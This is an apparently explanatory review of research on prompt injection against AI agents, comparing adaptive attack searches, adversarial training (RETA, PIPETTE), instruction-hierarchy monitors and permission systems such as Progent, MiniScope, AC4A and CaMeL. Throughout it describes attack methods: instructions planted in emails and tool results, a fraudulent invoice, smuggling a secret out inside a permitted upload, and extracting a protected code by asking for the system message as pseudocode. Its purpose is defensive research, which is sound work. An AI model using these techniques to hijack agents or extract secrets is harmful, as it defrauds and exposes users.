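The results for Meta SecAlign are more relevant to agents. Its developers had reported an attack success rate of 2% on AgentDojo's static attacks, and the adaptive search raised it to 96%. Nasr and colleagues also ran their search on models without added defences, including the Llama model that Meta SecAlign was built on.

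| Model | Utility | Static attack success | Search attack success | Median attempts to first success |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 57% | 35% | 100% | 14 |
| Meta SecAlign 70B | 73% | 5% | 96% | 37 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 74% | 30% | 100% | 13 |
| GPT-5 Mini | 72% | 0% | 75% | 58 |

The static figure for Meta SecAlign is 5% here because it comes from a single attack template on a different selection of cases. Training reduced that figure to a seventh of the original model's, but it reduced the adaptive search's success rate by only four percentage points. The typical successful search needed 37 attempts instead of 14, which would make little difference to an attacker with an automated search.

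GPT-5 Mini, which OpenAI later used as the starting point for its IH-Challenge experiment, resisted the static attack every time, but the search succeeded in 75% of cases. Nasr and colleagues expect that a larger budget would have raised that rate. The median in the table leaves out the cases where the search failed, so it understates how hard GPT-5 Mini was to attack.

Human attackers did better still. In the 29 scenarios that both people and the search attempted, the search succeeded in 69%. At least one person succeeded in every scenario, often out of several hundred who tried, and the best individual who attempted all 29 succeeded in 75%. Successful attempts could still be rare. With OpenAI's GPT-5 behind the Protect AI detector, for example, the share of submissions that succeeded rounds to 0.0%.

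### Fixed attacks and generated attacks

Nasr and colleagues blame the failure of the trained defences on the attacks used in training. The developers trained the model to resist a fixed set of attacks, and it did not learn to resist different ones. Researchers had already seen this problem in image classifiers, where training on a fixed set of distorted images failed against new distortions. Generating the distortions during training, always against the current version of the model, did work, but it protected only against the kinds of distortion used.

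Nasr and colleagues suggest that the same applies to language models, but did not train a model to test this. Two of them, Milad Nasr and Kai Xiao, later worked on IH-Challenge, which follows this method, since its attacker tests each message on the latest version of the defender.

*Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (He, Wang and colleagues, June 2026) introduced a training method called RETA. The researchers first trained an attacker model by reinforcement learning against an undefended agent and saved every attack that worked. They then trained the agent on those attacks, rewarding it for rejecting the attacker's task, completing the user's task and reasoning properly about the difference.

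To see which parts of the method mattered, they trained several versions of Qwen3-4B, a small open model, and attacked each with a genetic search like the one Nasr and colleagues used. The search succeeded on 57.5% of tasks against the original model and 50% against the version trained on fixed attacks. Training on the generated attacks lowered the success rate to 17.5%, and the full method lowered it to 7.5%. This supports the first half of the diagnosis, that training on fixed attacks does little to protect a model against new ones.

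Attacks generated for training need to be varied. An attacker model rewarded for each success tends to find one trick and repeat it in different words. In an earlier trial, He and colleagues added attacks from an existing method, RL-Hammer, to the training set, and the success rate of one kind of attack absent from that set rose from 25.7% to 30.7%.

*PIPETTE* (He, Wang et al., November 2026) found that training against a more successful attacker can leave a model more vulnerable than training against a less successful one. Against Qwen3-4B, RL-Hammer succeeded on 33% of the training tasks, while another attack method, PISmith, succeeded on 69%. But after reinforcement learning on PISmith's attacks, the defended model's worst-case attack success rate was 47.5%, compared with 27.5% after training on RL-Hammer's.

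Both RETA and PIPETTE deal with this by keeping a record of strategies. A language model reads each successful attack and describes how it redirects the agent, leaving out details such as names and account numbers. An algorithm reduces these descriptions to a small set of basic strategies, 32 in PIPETTE, and expresses each new attack as a combination of a few of them. The attacker earns an extra reward when the known strategies explain its new attack poorly. In PIPETTE, this reward is:

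r = Φ × (1 − ES)

Φ is 1 if the attack works and 0 if it fails, and ES is a score from 0 to 1 for how completely the known strategies explain the attack. A successful attack with ES = 0.25 receives a reward of 0.75, while a reworded version of a familiar attack, with ES close to 1, receives almost none. Multiplying by Φ gives failed attacks no reward, however novel they are.

### Checking actions against the user's task

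RETA and PIPETTE also train the agent to make two checks in its written reasoning before it acts: whether the latest tool result contains an attempt to redirect it, and whether each planned tool call serves the user's task. Under PIPETTE's version of the rule, the agent may use third-party content as data for the task but not as authority for a new goal.

In the invoice example, this rules out forwarding the user's private messages, whatever wording the stranger uses, because the user asked only for a payment. But a payment to the false account number still passes both checks, because the fraudulent email supplies only data.

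An agent can also apply the checks too strictly. He and colleagues found that in some of RETA's failures, the model refused to use any information from a tool result, even though the user's task depended on it. On Qwen3-4B under adaptive attack, the RETA agent completed 55.8% of the users' tasks. An agent trained with Meta SecAlign's method completed 69.2% but was hijacked about four times as often.

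PIPETTE tries to avoid this by giving feedback on individual tokens. During training, the developers know which text is the injection. They calculate how likely each of the agent's tokens would be if it had been told to ignore that text, and how likely if told to obey it. Training then favours the tokens that are more likely under the instruction to ignore it. This gives the agent more guidance than a single reward at the end, which would be the same for an agent that obeyed the attacker and one that stopped halfway through the user's task.

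He and colleagues tested PIPETTE on three models with two adaptive attacks. The table gives the results for the stronger attack, a genetic search.

| Model | Without added training | With an earlier trained defence | With PIPETTE |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 8B | 17.5% | 12.5% (Meta SecAlign) | 2.5% |
| Qwen3.6 27B | 70.0% | 30.0% (SecOPD) | 5.0% |
| GPT-OSS-20B | 92.5% | n/a | 10.0% |

OpenAI had already trained GPT-OSS-20B to follow an instruction hierarchy, but that gave it little protection against these attacks. The genetic search hijacked it on 37 of 40 tasks, and even static attacks succeeded 47% of the time on average. With PIPETTE, the genetic search succeeded on 4 of the 40 tasks, and the average success rate of static attacks fell to 2.2%. The success rate of the other adaptive attack, a tree search, fell from 50% to 5%. The model still completed 49.5% of ordinary tasks, down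 from 50.5%.

### Comparing the attackers' budgets

PIPETTE's 10% attack success rate is hard to compare with the 96% that Nasr and colleagues found for Meta SecAlign, because the attackers were very different. Nasr and colleagues allowed 800 attempts per case, while He and colleagues allowed about 250. That gap probably matters little, because most of the longer searches stopped improving after 100 to 200 attempts.

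The model writing the attacks matters more. Nasr and colleagues used Gemini 2.5 Pro with its maximum allowance for reasoning, while He and colleagues' PIPETTE test used Qwen3.5-4B, a small model that can run on a single graphics card. Attacks on Meta SecAlign succeeded 96% of the time with Gemini and 12.5% of the time with Qwen. The comparison isn't exact, because the Gemini attacks targeted a 70-billion-parameter version of SecAlign and the Qwen attacks an 8-billion-parameter version, which is hard to hijack partly because it is bad at completing tasks of any kind. Still, a defence that looks quite good in PIPETTE's test can fail almost completely against a better attacker.

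The attackers also differed in how much they knew about the defence. He et al. assume in principle that the attacker understands it, but their searches had no instructions specific to PIPETTE and relied only on the agent's behaviour for information about it. An attacker who knew about the two checks could try to make a malicious action look like part of the user's task. Against MELON, that kind of knowledge raised the attack success rate by 19 percentage points.

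PIPETTE was tested on 40 tasks on which static attacks had already hijacked an undefended model. This made the test harder for PIPETTE, so attacks may succeed less often on ordinary tasks. But 40 tasks is a small sample. If they were drawn at random from vulnerable tasks, four successful attacks would be compatible with a true success rate anywhere between about 4% and 23%.

RETA's average attack success rates over six adaptive attacks were 2.9% and 3.8% on the two models tested. These averages understate the risk, because a real attacker would use the best of the six, which succeeded on 7.5% and 5% of tasks.

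The fall from 92.5% to 10% on the same tasks, with the same attacker, is good evidence that training on varied attacks helps. It does not show how PIPETTE would do against Gemini 2.5 Pro or a few hundred people competing for prizes. It also does not settle the second half of the diagnosis, about generating attacks during training, because in both RETA and PIPETTE the attacker practised only on the undefended model, and its attacks were fixed before the defender's training began. A single pass of this kind cannot find weaknesses that appear only in the hardened model, as He and colleagues acknowledge.

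### Noticing, ranking and acting

An attack success rate shows how often a model fails but not why. In *Where Instruction Hierarchy Breaks*, Kariyappa and Suh of NVIDIA (2026) divide the model's job into three stages: noticing the relevant instructions, working out which one takes priority, and acting on that decision. They read the models' written reasoning to find the first stage that went wrong.

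The tests placed zero, four or eight harmless exchanges between a system message and a later user message that conflicted with it. One set of 541 examples involved rules such as using only lower case, and another of 1,860 involved attempts to extract protected information or override the system message.

The weak point varied by model. On the formatting rules, Qwen3.6-35B-A3B mostly made ranking errors when the two messages were adjacent, but it increasingly failed to notice the system message's rule as the conversation grew longer. On the protected information, it failed mainly in ranking, whereas Claude Sonnet 4.6 failed mainly in acting, meaning its reasoning reached the right decision but its answer still broke the rule.

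In one example of a failure to act, the system message contained a secret access code and an instruction never to reveal it. The user asked the model to rewrite the system message's instructions as pseudocode, an informal outline of a program. The model wrote in its reasoning that the code must not appear, but included it in the pseudocode. He et al. saw the same failure in agents trained with RETA. In some successful attacks, the model wrote that the planted instruction was untrusted and then made the requested tool call.

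This evidence is limited because written reasoning is an imperfect record of how a model reaches its answer, as Kariyappa and Suh acknowledge, and because they used another language model to sort the failures. Their diagnosis covers conflicts between system and user messages, so the proportions of failures could differ for instructions in emails and web pages.

Researchers found that models are much better at spotting a conflict between instructions than at handling it correctly. In one test, the system message told Gemma 4 31B, an open Google model, to answer only in English, and the user later asked for French. The model obeyed the system message 61.7% of the time when one exchange separated the two instructions, but never when eight did. Yet when the researchers asked it directly whether the messages conflicted, it was almost always right.

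Kariyappa and Suh therefore had each model check itself. One monitor checks the conversation for conflicts while the model prepares its answer, and if it finds one, the model starts again with a warning. Another checks the draft answer, and the model rewrites the draft if it breaks a higher-ranked rule. With OpenAI's GPT-5.3, the better monitor cut violations of the formatting rules by 86%. Under adaptive attack, the best reduction in successful attacks was 45%, although the attacker had only eight attempts per example.

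The monitor that checks for conflicts flagged almost all of the attacks that still succeeded, but the model broke the rule despite receiving the warning. A program that withheld the answer whenever the monitor flagged a conflict would have stopped nearly all of these attacks. However, it would also have withheld some harmless answers, and attackers would then have tried to fool the monitor too.

### Results for newer models

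McCauley and colleagues, at the AI security company HiddenLayer, tested 32 model configurations on 2,688 scenarios in July 2026. In 2,323 scenarios, a lower-ranked message conflicts with a higher-ranked requirement. The other 365 contain no conflict and test whether the model can do the task at all. On average, models obeyed the system message over the user 84.6% of the time, but the user over a tool result only 69.6% of the time. Models that did well on the first kind of conflict did not always do well on the second. Grok 4.20, from xAI, scored 92.7% when the user challenged the system message and 61.2% when the conflicting instruction came from a tool.

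The next table shows how often models resisted instructions planted in tool results.

| What the planted instruction tries to change | Average of 32 | Claude Opus 4.6 | GPT 5.4 | Grok 4.20 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| What information the agent discloses | 80.3% | 100% | 100% | 46.7% |
| Which actions it takes | 77.7% | 100% | 99.6% | 46.2% |
| The arguments and targets of its tool calls | 76.7% | 100% | 99.3% | 80.1% |
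| The accuracy and completeness of its answer | 66.7% | 100% | 98.0% | 75.8% |
| Whether it carries out the user's task | 66.6% | 100% | 98.8% | 65.5% |
| The language and format of its answer | 49.8% | 100% | 87.6% | 52.8% |

On average, models were better at resisting instructions to take unauthorised actions than instructions to change what they told the user. When a tool result contained instructions to misreport the tool's findings, they resisted only 45.4% of the time. A permission system that checks tool calls would not catch this, because the agent can mislead its user without making any forbidden call.

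Other failures would be easy to prevent outside the model. When the system message banned all tool calls and the user's request invited one, models obeyed the ban only 53.2% of the time. A developer who wants no tool calls can prevent them by not giving the model any tools.

Warning models in the system message that tool results are untrusted helped some far more than others. Without a warning, Grok 4.20 and Amazon's Nova 2 Lite both resisted about 31% of planted instructions. With a detailed warning, Grok resisted 88.9% and Nova only 35.2%. Developers therefore cannot assume that a warning that works for one model will protect another.

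Claude Opus 4.6's perfect score is the best result in the table, but McCauley and colleagues wrote all the scenarios in advance. GPT-5 Mini also had a perfect record against a static attack before Nasr and colleagues' search succeeded against it in 75% of cases. The benchmark did not include an adaptive search against Opus 4.6 or GPT 5.4, and Anthropic and OpenAI have released newer models since. Kariyappa and Suh ran adaptive tests on GPT-5.3 and Claude Sonnet 4.6, but they allowed only eight attempts and did not test an agent with tools.

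A fixed benchmark is still useful for ruling models out. Qwen 3 235B-A22B resisted only 5.4% of the instructions planted in tool results, which is enough to show, without an adaptive attack, that it is unsafe to let it both read strangers' emails and make payments. A high score is harder to interpret. Nasr and colleagues point out that an evaluation cannot prove that a defence is robust, and can at most show that determined attempts to break it failed.

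## Progent: a permission policy for each task

To pay the plumber, an assistant must read strangers' emails and send money, even if its model sometimes obeys the wrong instruction. Progent, a permission system from researchers at two University of California campuses and the National University of Singapore, controls the agent's tool calls without changing the model. AgentDojo's tool filter could only remove whole tools, but Progent can also restrict how the agent uses the remaining tools, for example by limiting payments to one account.

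### Rules and checks

In *Progent* (2025), Shi, He and colleagues define a policy as a list of rules. Each rule allows or forbids calls to one tool and can set conditions on their arguments. A condition can compare numbers, check whether a value is in a list, or match text against a pattern.

Suppose the assistant has found the plumber's invoice, a bill for £180 with the account number 4471. In simplified notation, a suitable policy would be:

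```
allow search_emails   when query contains "invoice"
allow read_email      for any message
allow send_money      when recipient = 4471 and amount ≤ 180
```

The assistant now calls the payment tool with recipient 4471 and amount 180. Progent selects the rules for that tool and checks any "forbid" rules first. There are none, so it checks the "allow" rule. Both conditions hold, so it allows the payment.

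The assistant then follows the instructions in the stranger's email and tries to send the user's private messages to an outside address. No rule covers the tool for sending mail, and Progent blocks any call that no rule allows. It returns an error message that gives the reason and repeats the user's request, so the assistant can carry on with the task. A rule can also make Progent stop the agent or ask the user what to do.

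This check doesn't use a language model, so the same call under the same policy always gets the same result, however persuasive the stranger's email was.

### How the policy changes during a task

Nobody could have written the third rule when the user typed the request, because the account number was still in the mailbox. Shi and colleagues therefore have a language model write an initial policy from the user's request and the list of tools, before it sees any outside text. The model then revises the policy as the agent learns more.

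A policy revision takes two steps. After a tool call, the model first decides whether the result might justify a change. It sees the call but not the result, so an attacker's text cannot influence this decision. If a change might be justified, the model then reads the result and proposes a new policy. Text in the result, such as a stranger's email, can influence the model at this second step.

Progent guards against this with an SMT solver, a program that works out whether any values can satisfy a logical formula. Let A(P) be the set of all tool calls that policy P allows. For a proposed policy P′, the solver checks whether

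A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

If the old policy already allowed every call that the new one allows, the change is a narrowing, and Progent applies it automatically. Any other change is an expansion and needs approval. Lowering the payment limit from £180 to £150 is a narrowing, but raising it to £500 is an expansion because it would newly allow a payment of £400. Replacing account 4471 with a different account is also an expansion, even though the policy still permits only one recipient.

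Between approvals, the set of permitted calls can shrink but never grow, a property Shi and colleagues call monotonic confinement. This addresses a concern raised in *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) that malicious text in a tool result could cause the update mechanism to loosen the policy. The model can still propose a looser policy, but somebody has to approve it.

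A person can approve or deny each expansion, or a setting can accept them all, deny them all, or treat some tools differently from others. An organisation can also write fixed rules that Progent applies before the policy for the task. If a company's rules forbid payments above £1,000, no policy written by the model can override that.

### An attack that stays within the policy

Suppose the assistant finds the fraudster's fake invoice, with account number 9902, before the real one. If the policy does not yet allow payments, the model proposes a rule for paying 9902. The solver correctly reports that the rule would expand the policy, and Progent asks the user to approve it. But the user expects to approve a payment and has probably never seen the plumber's account number, so the request looks legitimate.

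The initial policy might instead allow payments to anyone, since the user asked for a payment. After reading the false invoice, the model could restrict the recipient to 9902. Progent applies this update without asking anybody because it narrows the policy. The update gives the fraudster no new permission, since the initial policy already allowed a payment to 9902, but it blocks the payment to the plumber, which was the only correct way to finish the task.

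Shi and colleagues say that Progent cannot stop attacks that use only the permissions a task needs. They left two such attacks, both of which steer the agent towards a different hotel, out of their AgentDojo tests. They argued that an attacker who controls the information can change it, and that even a person could not tell. This is a reasonable limit for a permission system, but it means their results do not cover the false invoice.

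An attacker can also misuse a permitted channel by changing what is sent through it. In *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026), Singh and Srinivasa tested a coding agent that had to upload a status report to an approved service. The agent also received a planted instruction to include a file containing a secret. The policy checked only the destination, so the secret went through with the report.

Checking the contents was hard. A rule that searched each upload for complete lines from the secret file missed two attacks because they sent the secret value without the rest of its line. In a small follow-up, requiring the report to match one exact text blocked the attacks but also blocked legitimate reports with slightly different formatting. A version that ignored formatting differences let those reports through and still blocked the attacks, but Singh and Srinivasa ran it only four times. They tested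 a simple policy of their own, not Progent, but a Progent rule that fixes a message's recipient and leaves the body open has the same weakness.

### Results on two benchmarks

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo and on Agent Security Bench (ASB), which has ten scenarios and five attack templates. OpenAI's GPT-4o acted as the agent and wrote the policies. Singh and Srinivasa give the exact utility figures for AgentDojo.

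| Measure | No defence | Progent |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, attack success | 39.9% | 1.0% |
| AgentDojo, utility without attacks | 79.4% | 76.3% |
| AgentDojo, utility under attack | 54.0% | 61.3% |
| ASB, attack success | 70.3% | 3.9% |

Utility on ASB stayed about the same. On AgentDojo, Progent lowered utility by about three percentage points when there was no attack and raised it by seven when there was one.

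In these tests, Shi and colleagues had the approver accept every expansion to imitate a careless user, so monotonic confinement did not contribute to the main results. The low attack success rates show that GPT-4o usually wrote sensible policies even after reading the planted text.

The Progent paper also compares other ways of handling policy updates on AgentDojo. With the initial policy fixed for the whole task, attack success was 2.5%. Allowing updates that narrowed the policy but refusing any that expanded it brought attack success slightly below the 1.0% of the main test, but also reduced utility. Having a human review the initial policy and every expansion reduced attack success to zero. But the experiment assumed that the reviewer would never allow unrestricted payments and would reject any malicious address, although in the invoice example the hard part is recognising the malicious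 account.

Only 6% of policy updates were expansions, so a reviewer would have few requests to answer. But AgentDojo's tasks are short, and the experiment permanently allowed harmless read-only tools. A user with longer and more varied tasks might see more requests.

The attacks that succeeded on ASB mostly used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate tools. The model that wrote the policy could not tell them apart, and Shi and colleagues doubt that a person could without knowing in advance which tools to trust. Rules written by hand with that knowledge reduced the attack success rate to zero.

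Progent also helped models that already resisted injections. On AgentDojo, attack success fell from 4.8% to 0.3% for Meta SecAlign and from 6.8% to 0.5% for Claude Sonnet 4. These attacks were static, so the result does not show how these models with Progent would do against an adaptive search like the one Nasr and colleagues later used to break Meta SecAlign.

Shi and colleagues tried three adaptive attacks on Progent, again with every expansion approved. Two added a request for the model to permit the attacker's tools, and the third used AgentVigil, an automated method for finding injections. The attack success rate rose only slightly.

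### An independent test on a small model

In *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026), Narisetty, Kore and colleagues repeated the experiment with Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, as both agent and policy writer. They are independent of Progent's developers, but they have a commercial interest in the approach because they work at LaunchSafe, a company that builds security tools of the same general kind.

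The evaluation combined the first eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo settings with all the injection tasks, and was run three times. It left out the travel setting because the small model got stuck in very long loops. The adaptive attack presented the malicious action as a routine step that the user had already authorised, to try to get the policy writer to allow it.

| Setting | Attack success, no defence | Attack success, Progent | Adaptive attack success, Progent | Utility under attack, no defence | Utility under attack, Progent |
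|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% | 31.9% | 31.9% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% | 47.5% | 20.8% |
| Workspace | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 56.3% | 28.5% |
| Average | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% | 45.2% | 27.1% |

Average attack success fell from 25.8% to 4.2%, which confirms that the method can work with a much weaker model than GPT-4o. These averages include the workspace setting, where the undefended agent ignored every attack. Without that setting, attack success fell from 38.7% to 6.4%.

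The adaptive attack result is less informative. The attack did worse on average than the ordinary one, and Narisetty and colleagues suggest that its gentler wording made the agent less likely to obey. Even if an attack persuades the policy writer, it fails if the agent ignores it. They tried only one handwritten template, which is a much weaker test than the automated searches Nasr and colleagues ran against trained defences. They also did not test attacks that use only tools the policy already allowed, which they name as the next experiment.

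Progent reduced utility by two fifths here, and the defended agent needed about 15 times as many model calls per task. In the workspace setting, Progent halved utility even though no attacks had succeeded without it. The small model probably caused the drop by writing poor policies, since utility hardly fell in the GPT-4o tests, but Narisetty and colleagues did not test a stronger policy writer with the same agent.

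### Applying the policy to a command line

AgentDojo gives the agent separate tools for payments, email and other tasks, with arguments that a rule can check. Many coding agents instead do most of their work through a command line, where one tool can run almost anything. *INFUSE* (Nguyen, Guo and colleagues, 2026) presents a benchmark for such agents, with 40 tasks and 56 attacks in files, terminal output and other places the agent reads. The agent writes one shell command per turn, and the benchmark runs it in an isolated container.

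Progent's rules do not fit this arrangement directly, so Nguyen and colleagues adapted them. Their software breaks each command into the programs it runs and the places it sends or writes data, then checks those parts against a list of permissions derived from the user's task. It replaces a blocked command with a fixed placeholder. They kept Progent's form of policy and still block anything the policy does not allow. They do not mention policy updates, the solver or an approver when describing the adaptation.

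They tested five models on 200 combinations of task and attack.

| Model | Attack success, no defence | Attack success, adapted Progent | Utility, no defence | Utility, adapted Progent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-14B | 27.3% | 35.0% | 48.5% | 43.5% |
| Gemma 3 12B | 32.7% | 30.5% | 23.6% | 6.0% |
| GPT-4o mini | 46.5% | 43.0% | 54.0% | 17.0% |
| Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | 55.5% | 63.5% | 71.5% | 25.5% |
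| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 6.5% | 27.1% | n/a | n/a |

For the first four models, the changes in attack success were too small to distinguish from chance. Utility fell by 64–75% on three of them. The adapted policy therefore blocked a lot of legitimate work and few attacks, if any.

One reason may be the kinds of attack involved, which include telling the agent to lower a version number, add a line to a configuration file, or require an outdated software package. An agent fixing a project edits similar files with the same commands, so a policy that allows the user's task will often allow the attack too. An attacker has many more ways to stay within the policy on a command line than in a banking application with a separate payment tool.

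The fixed list of permissions probably causes the loss of utility, because a programmer looking for a bug cannot predict every command the search will require. In the original system, the policy can grow with approval, and a blocked agent receives an explanation instead of a placeholder.

The rise for Claude Sonnet 4.6 is harder to explain, and Nguyen and colleagues do not give a cause. They warn that Sonnet's low attack success rate on the full benchmark came from runs that hit a spending limit, and should not count as evidence of resistance. If the same happened in this comparison, many undefended runs may have stopped before the agent could act on an injection. Blocked commands produce little output, which makes each turn cheaper, so the defended agent may have got further before reaching the limit. That would explain the rise even if the policy did not make Sonnet more likely to follow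 injected instructions, but nobody has tested this explanation.

The scoring may also understate what the policy prevented. A language model judged each run and was told to count it as compromised if the agent followed the injection even partially. A run could therefore count as compromised because the agent tried to run the attacker's command, even if the policy blocked that command. Shi and colleagues found a similar problem in one AgentDojo task, where the benchmark counted a blocked call as a successful attack, and they corrected those results by hand. Nguyen and colleagues also measure actual damage, such as altered files, but do not report that measure for this comparison.

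For these reasons, the result is weak evidence that Progent makes agents less safe, and Nguyen and colleagues limit their conclusion to their own adaptation. It is better evidence that permission rules are much less useful when one tool can do everything. In the same environment, Meta SecAlign's training cut attack success from 29.6% to 7.8% for a 70-billion-parameter model, so the trained defence worked better than the external one against these static attacks.

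Developers may run into the same problem when they add Progent to an existing coding agent. Progent can run as a proxy, a separate program between the agent and its outside tools, so developers don't have to change the agent. But Shi and colleagues note that the proxy cannot check tools built into the agent, which in a coding agent may include the command line.

### The problem of writing policies

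Progent's check is reliable, but its protection depends on the policy. A person can write good rules for a task known in advance, but not for every request a user might make. A model can write rules for each request, but it may misinterpret the task or be misled by a stranger's email. In *Agent-Sentry* (2026), Sequeira, Damianakis and colleagues object that Progent needs a separate policy for each agent, and that using a model to write it gives attackers another target and still requires manual corrections.

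Their own system instead learns what an agent normally does from past runs, including where the arguments of its tool calls usually come from. It blocked 94.3% of successful injections on AgentDojo and a related benchmark, and allowed 95.1% of legitimate runs. Nobody has to write rules, but the system needs a record of good behaviour and uses a language model to decide unclear cases. Sequeira and colleagues also exclude ambiguous requests, such as "pay the bill" when there are several invoices.

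*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) points out that least privilege applies at several levels, including which tools the agent can see, which call it may make at each step, and which arguments it may use. Finer levels give better protection but require more decisions from whoever writes the policy. The paper also argues that tests should measure wrongly blocked actions and the burden on users as well as prevented attacks.

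### MiniScope: permissions from the services themselves

*MiniScope* (Zhu, Tseng and colleagues, 2025) reduces the number of decisions by using permissions that already exist. Services such as Gmail and Slack give other programs access to a user's account through OAuth, a standard that doesn't require sharing the password. Each service groups its functions into scopes. One scope might cover reading mail, while a broader one also covers sending and deleting it.

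MiniScope reads the service's public documentation and arranges the scopes in a hierarchy. If one scope allows everything that another allows and more, it goes above the other. The names can be misleading, so MiniScope compares the actual lists of functions. When the agent submits a plan, a solver chooses the cheapest set of scopes that covers every call in it:

minimise Σ cost(s) · x(s), with at least one chosen scope covering each call

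x(s) is 1 if the solver chooses scope s and 0 otherwise, and the cost is the number of functions the scope allows. The calculation is necessary because scopes overlap. In Google Calendar, for example, 24 of the 37 functions are available through more than one branch of the hierarchy.

If the plan needs a scope that the agent does not have, MiniScope asks the user for permission, much as a phone does when an app requests camera access. The user can refuse, or allow it once, for the current session, or always. MiniScope keeps the account credentials itself and checks each call before passing it to the service, so the agent cannot bypass the check by using the credentials directly.

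In one of the paper's examples, a user asks the agent to answer an email about a film night. The email includes an instruction to delete the message after replying. The agent adds the deletion to its plan, and MiniScope asks the user for full access to Gmail. The user refuses, because replying to an email should not require that much access.

The solver finds the smallest set of permissions for the agent's plan, which may differ from what the user asked for. If an injection has already changed the plan, the solver finds the least access the attack needs, and only the user can notice that something is wrong. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) adds that Zhu and colleagues do not discuss whether there is always a single best set. Two sets might each be minimal but allow different things, and the choice then depends on the measure being minimised. Counting the permitted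 functions is a crude measure because it treats reading a message and deleting one as equally serious.

Zhu and colleagues tested MiniScope with made-up requests for ten real applications. It added 1–6% to the agent's running time, excluding the time users spent answering questions. When they had language models choose the permissions instead, the best commercial models agreed with MiniScope's solver 70–83% of the time, and most of their mistakes granted too much access. For tasks involving several applications, using a model took about 20 seconds per request, compared with five for MiniScope.

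The solver also found excessive permissions in products already in use. ChatGPT's Gmail connector, for example, requested access to 50 functions when its advertised features needed only 32. The extra access let it change and delete emails, although it was described as read-only.

To estimate the burden on users, Zhu and colleagues simulated three months of Gmail use by people with different habits. MiniScope asked for confirmation on 18–60% of requests, depending on the type of user. A simulated user who always chose "always allow" answered a few questions at the start and none later. For such a user, the stranger's forwarding attack would succeed without warning, because the assistant would already have permanent permission to send mail.

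These experiments measure excess permissions, delay and interruptions, but not how many attacks succeed. MiniScope also relies on other defences to stop attacks within an approved scope. If a bank has one scope for making payments, the user can decide whether the assistant may make payments, but not to whom. Once the user approves that scope, any account number passes the check, including the false one.

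### AC4A: permissions on parts of an account

*AC4A* (Sharma and Grossman, 2026) makes permissions more precise by attaching them to the resources an agent can reach instead of to its tools. For example, it divides a calendar into years, months and days. A user can let the agent read June 2026, and this permission covers every day in June but does not let the agent read July or add anything to June.

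The application's developer writes a function that translates each call into the permissions it needs. A second function compares these with the permissions the user has granted:

difference(needed, granted) → remaining

AC4A subtracts each granted permission in turn from the permissions a call needs, and allows the call if nothing remains. Otherwise, it blocks the call, and the user can see which permission is missing. For example, if the assistant needs to read June and July but has permission only for June, July remains and AC4A blocks the call.

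The same permissions apply when the agent uses a website. A configuration file links parts of the page to parts of the account, and AC4A covers the parts of the page that the agent may not see or use. In one demonstration, an agent checked a calendar and then booked a flight. It could search for flights once the user allowed it to read flight information, but it needed separate permissions to book Delta flight 1847 and to read the user's credit card details. Advertisements for car hire stayed covered throughout.

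With Progent, a company would need separate rules for every tool that can reach the calendar. With AC4A, it would need only one permission, but somebody must correctly describe how each tool and web page uses the calendar. Sharma and Grossman consider this reliance on correct descriptions the system's most serious practical limitation. They wrote a working description of Outlook's web calendar without Microsoft's help, but a change in the page's design could break it. Any part of a web page that the description leaves out stays visible, so an omission exposes information. Progent, by default, blocks whatever its policy doesn't mention.

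AC4A also leaves the choice of permissions to someone else. Users can select them from a menu or describe them in ordinary language for a model to translate. When AC4A blocks a call, the agent can ask the user, try another approach, or have a model suggest the missing permission for the user to approve. In a fourth mode, called "YOLO", the model grants whatever permissions the agent needs without the user's approval. Sharma and Grossman say this mode is not secure at all and is suitable only for experiments or record-keeping.

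For the plumber's invoice, AC4A could limit the assistant to creating a payment to account 4471, if the bank had described its accounts in this way. It cannot yet express a condition such as a maximum amount, which Progent can do easily. Its permissions also last until the user removes them, so the assistant could pay the plumber again next month without being asked. Sharma and Grossman suggest permissions that expire after one use, but have not settled who would decide when a permission expires. They demonstrated AC4A only on a game and the flight booking, and report neither an attack success rate nor utility, so its effect on real attacks is unknown.

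## CaMeL: keeping untrusted text out of the plan

Progent checks an agent's tool calls, but the model that chooses those calls still reads strangers' emails, and so does the model that revises the policy. In CaMeL, a system from Google, Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich, the model that decides what the agent will do never sees text from outside. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced CaMeL in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (March 2025). Edoardo Debenedetti had also led the work on AgentDojo.

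### Two models and an interpreter

CaMeL's planning model receives only the user's request and descriptions of the tools. It uses these to write a complete program in a restricted form of Python. A second model, the reading model, handles untrusted text and has no tools. When the program needs a fact from an email, it passes the email to the reading model with a question and the form the answer must take, such as a number or an email address.

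An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program line by line. It records where each value came from and who may read it, and it checks every tool call against a policy before making it.

The programmer Simon Willison had proposed the split between two models in 2023, but in his version an attacker could still trick the reading model into supplying the attacker's address, which the plan would then use. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, credits CaMeL with fixing this flaw by tracking values and checking policies. He adds that CaMeL could improve privacy, because reading is easier than planning, so a small reading model could run on the user's own computer and the company that hosts the planning model would never see the emails.

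### The plumber's invoice, line by line

The user again asks the assistant to find the plumber's invoice and pay it. The planning model has not seen the mailbox, but it knows that an invoice has an amount and an account number. In simplified notation, it might write:

```
emails  = search_emails("plumber invoice")
invoice = ask_reading_model("Find the plumber's invoice", emails,
                            answer = {account: number, amount: number})
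send_money(recipient = invoice.account, amount = invoice.amount)
```

The first line searches the mailbox. Suppose the results include the plumber's invoice, which lists £180 and account 4471, and the stranger's email ordering the agent to forward private messages. The interpreter stores both and labels them as text from outside, without passing either to the planning model.

The second line gives the emails to the reading model. This model may well follow the stranger's instructions, since it is no more resistant to injection than any other model. But it has no tool for forwarding anything, and its answer must be two numbers, so the worst it can do is return the wrong numbers. The interpreter labels both numbers as derived from the emails.

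The third and last line requests the payment. None of the three lines sends mail, and no email can add a fourth, so the forwarding attack fails whatever the stranger writes. Progent stops the same attack by blocking a call that the agent has already tried to make.

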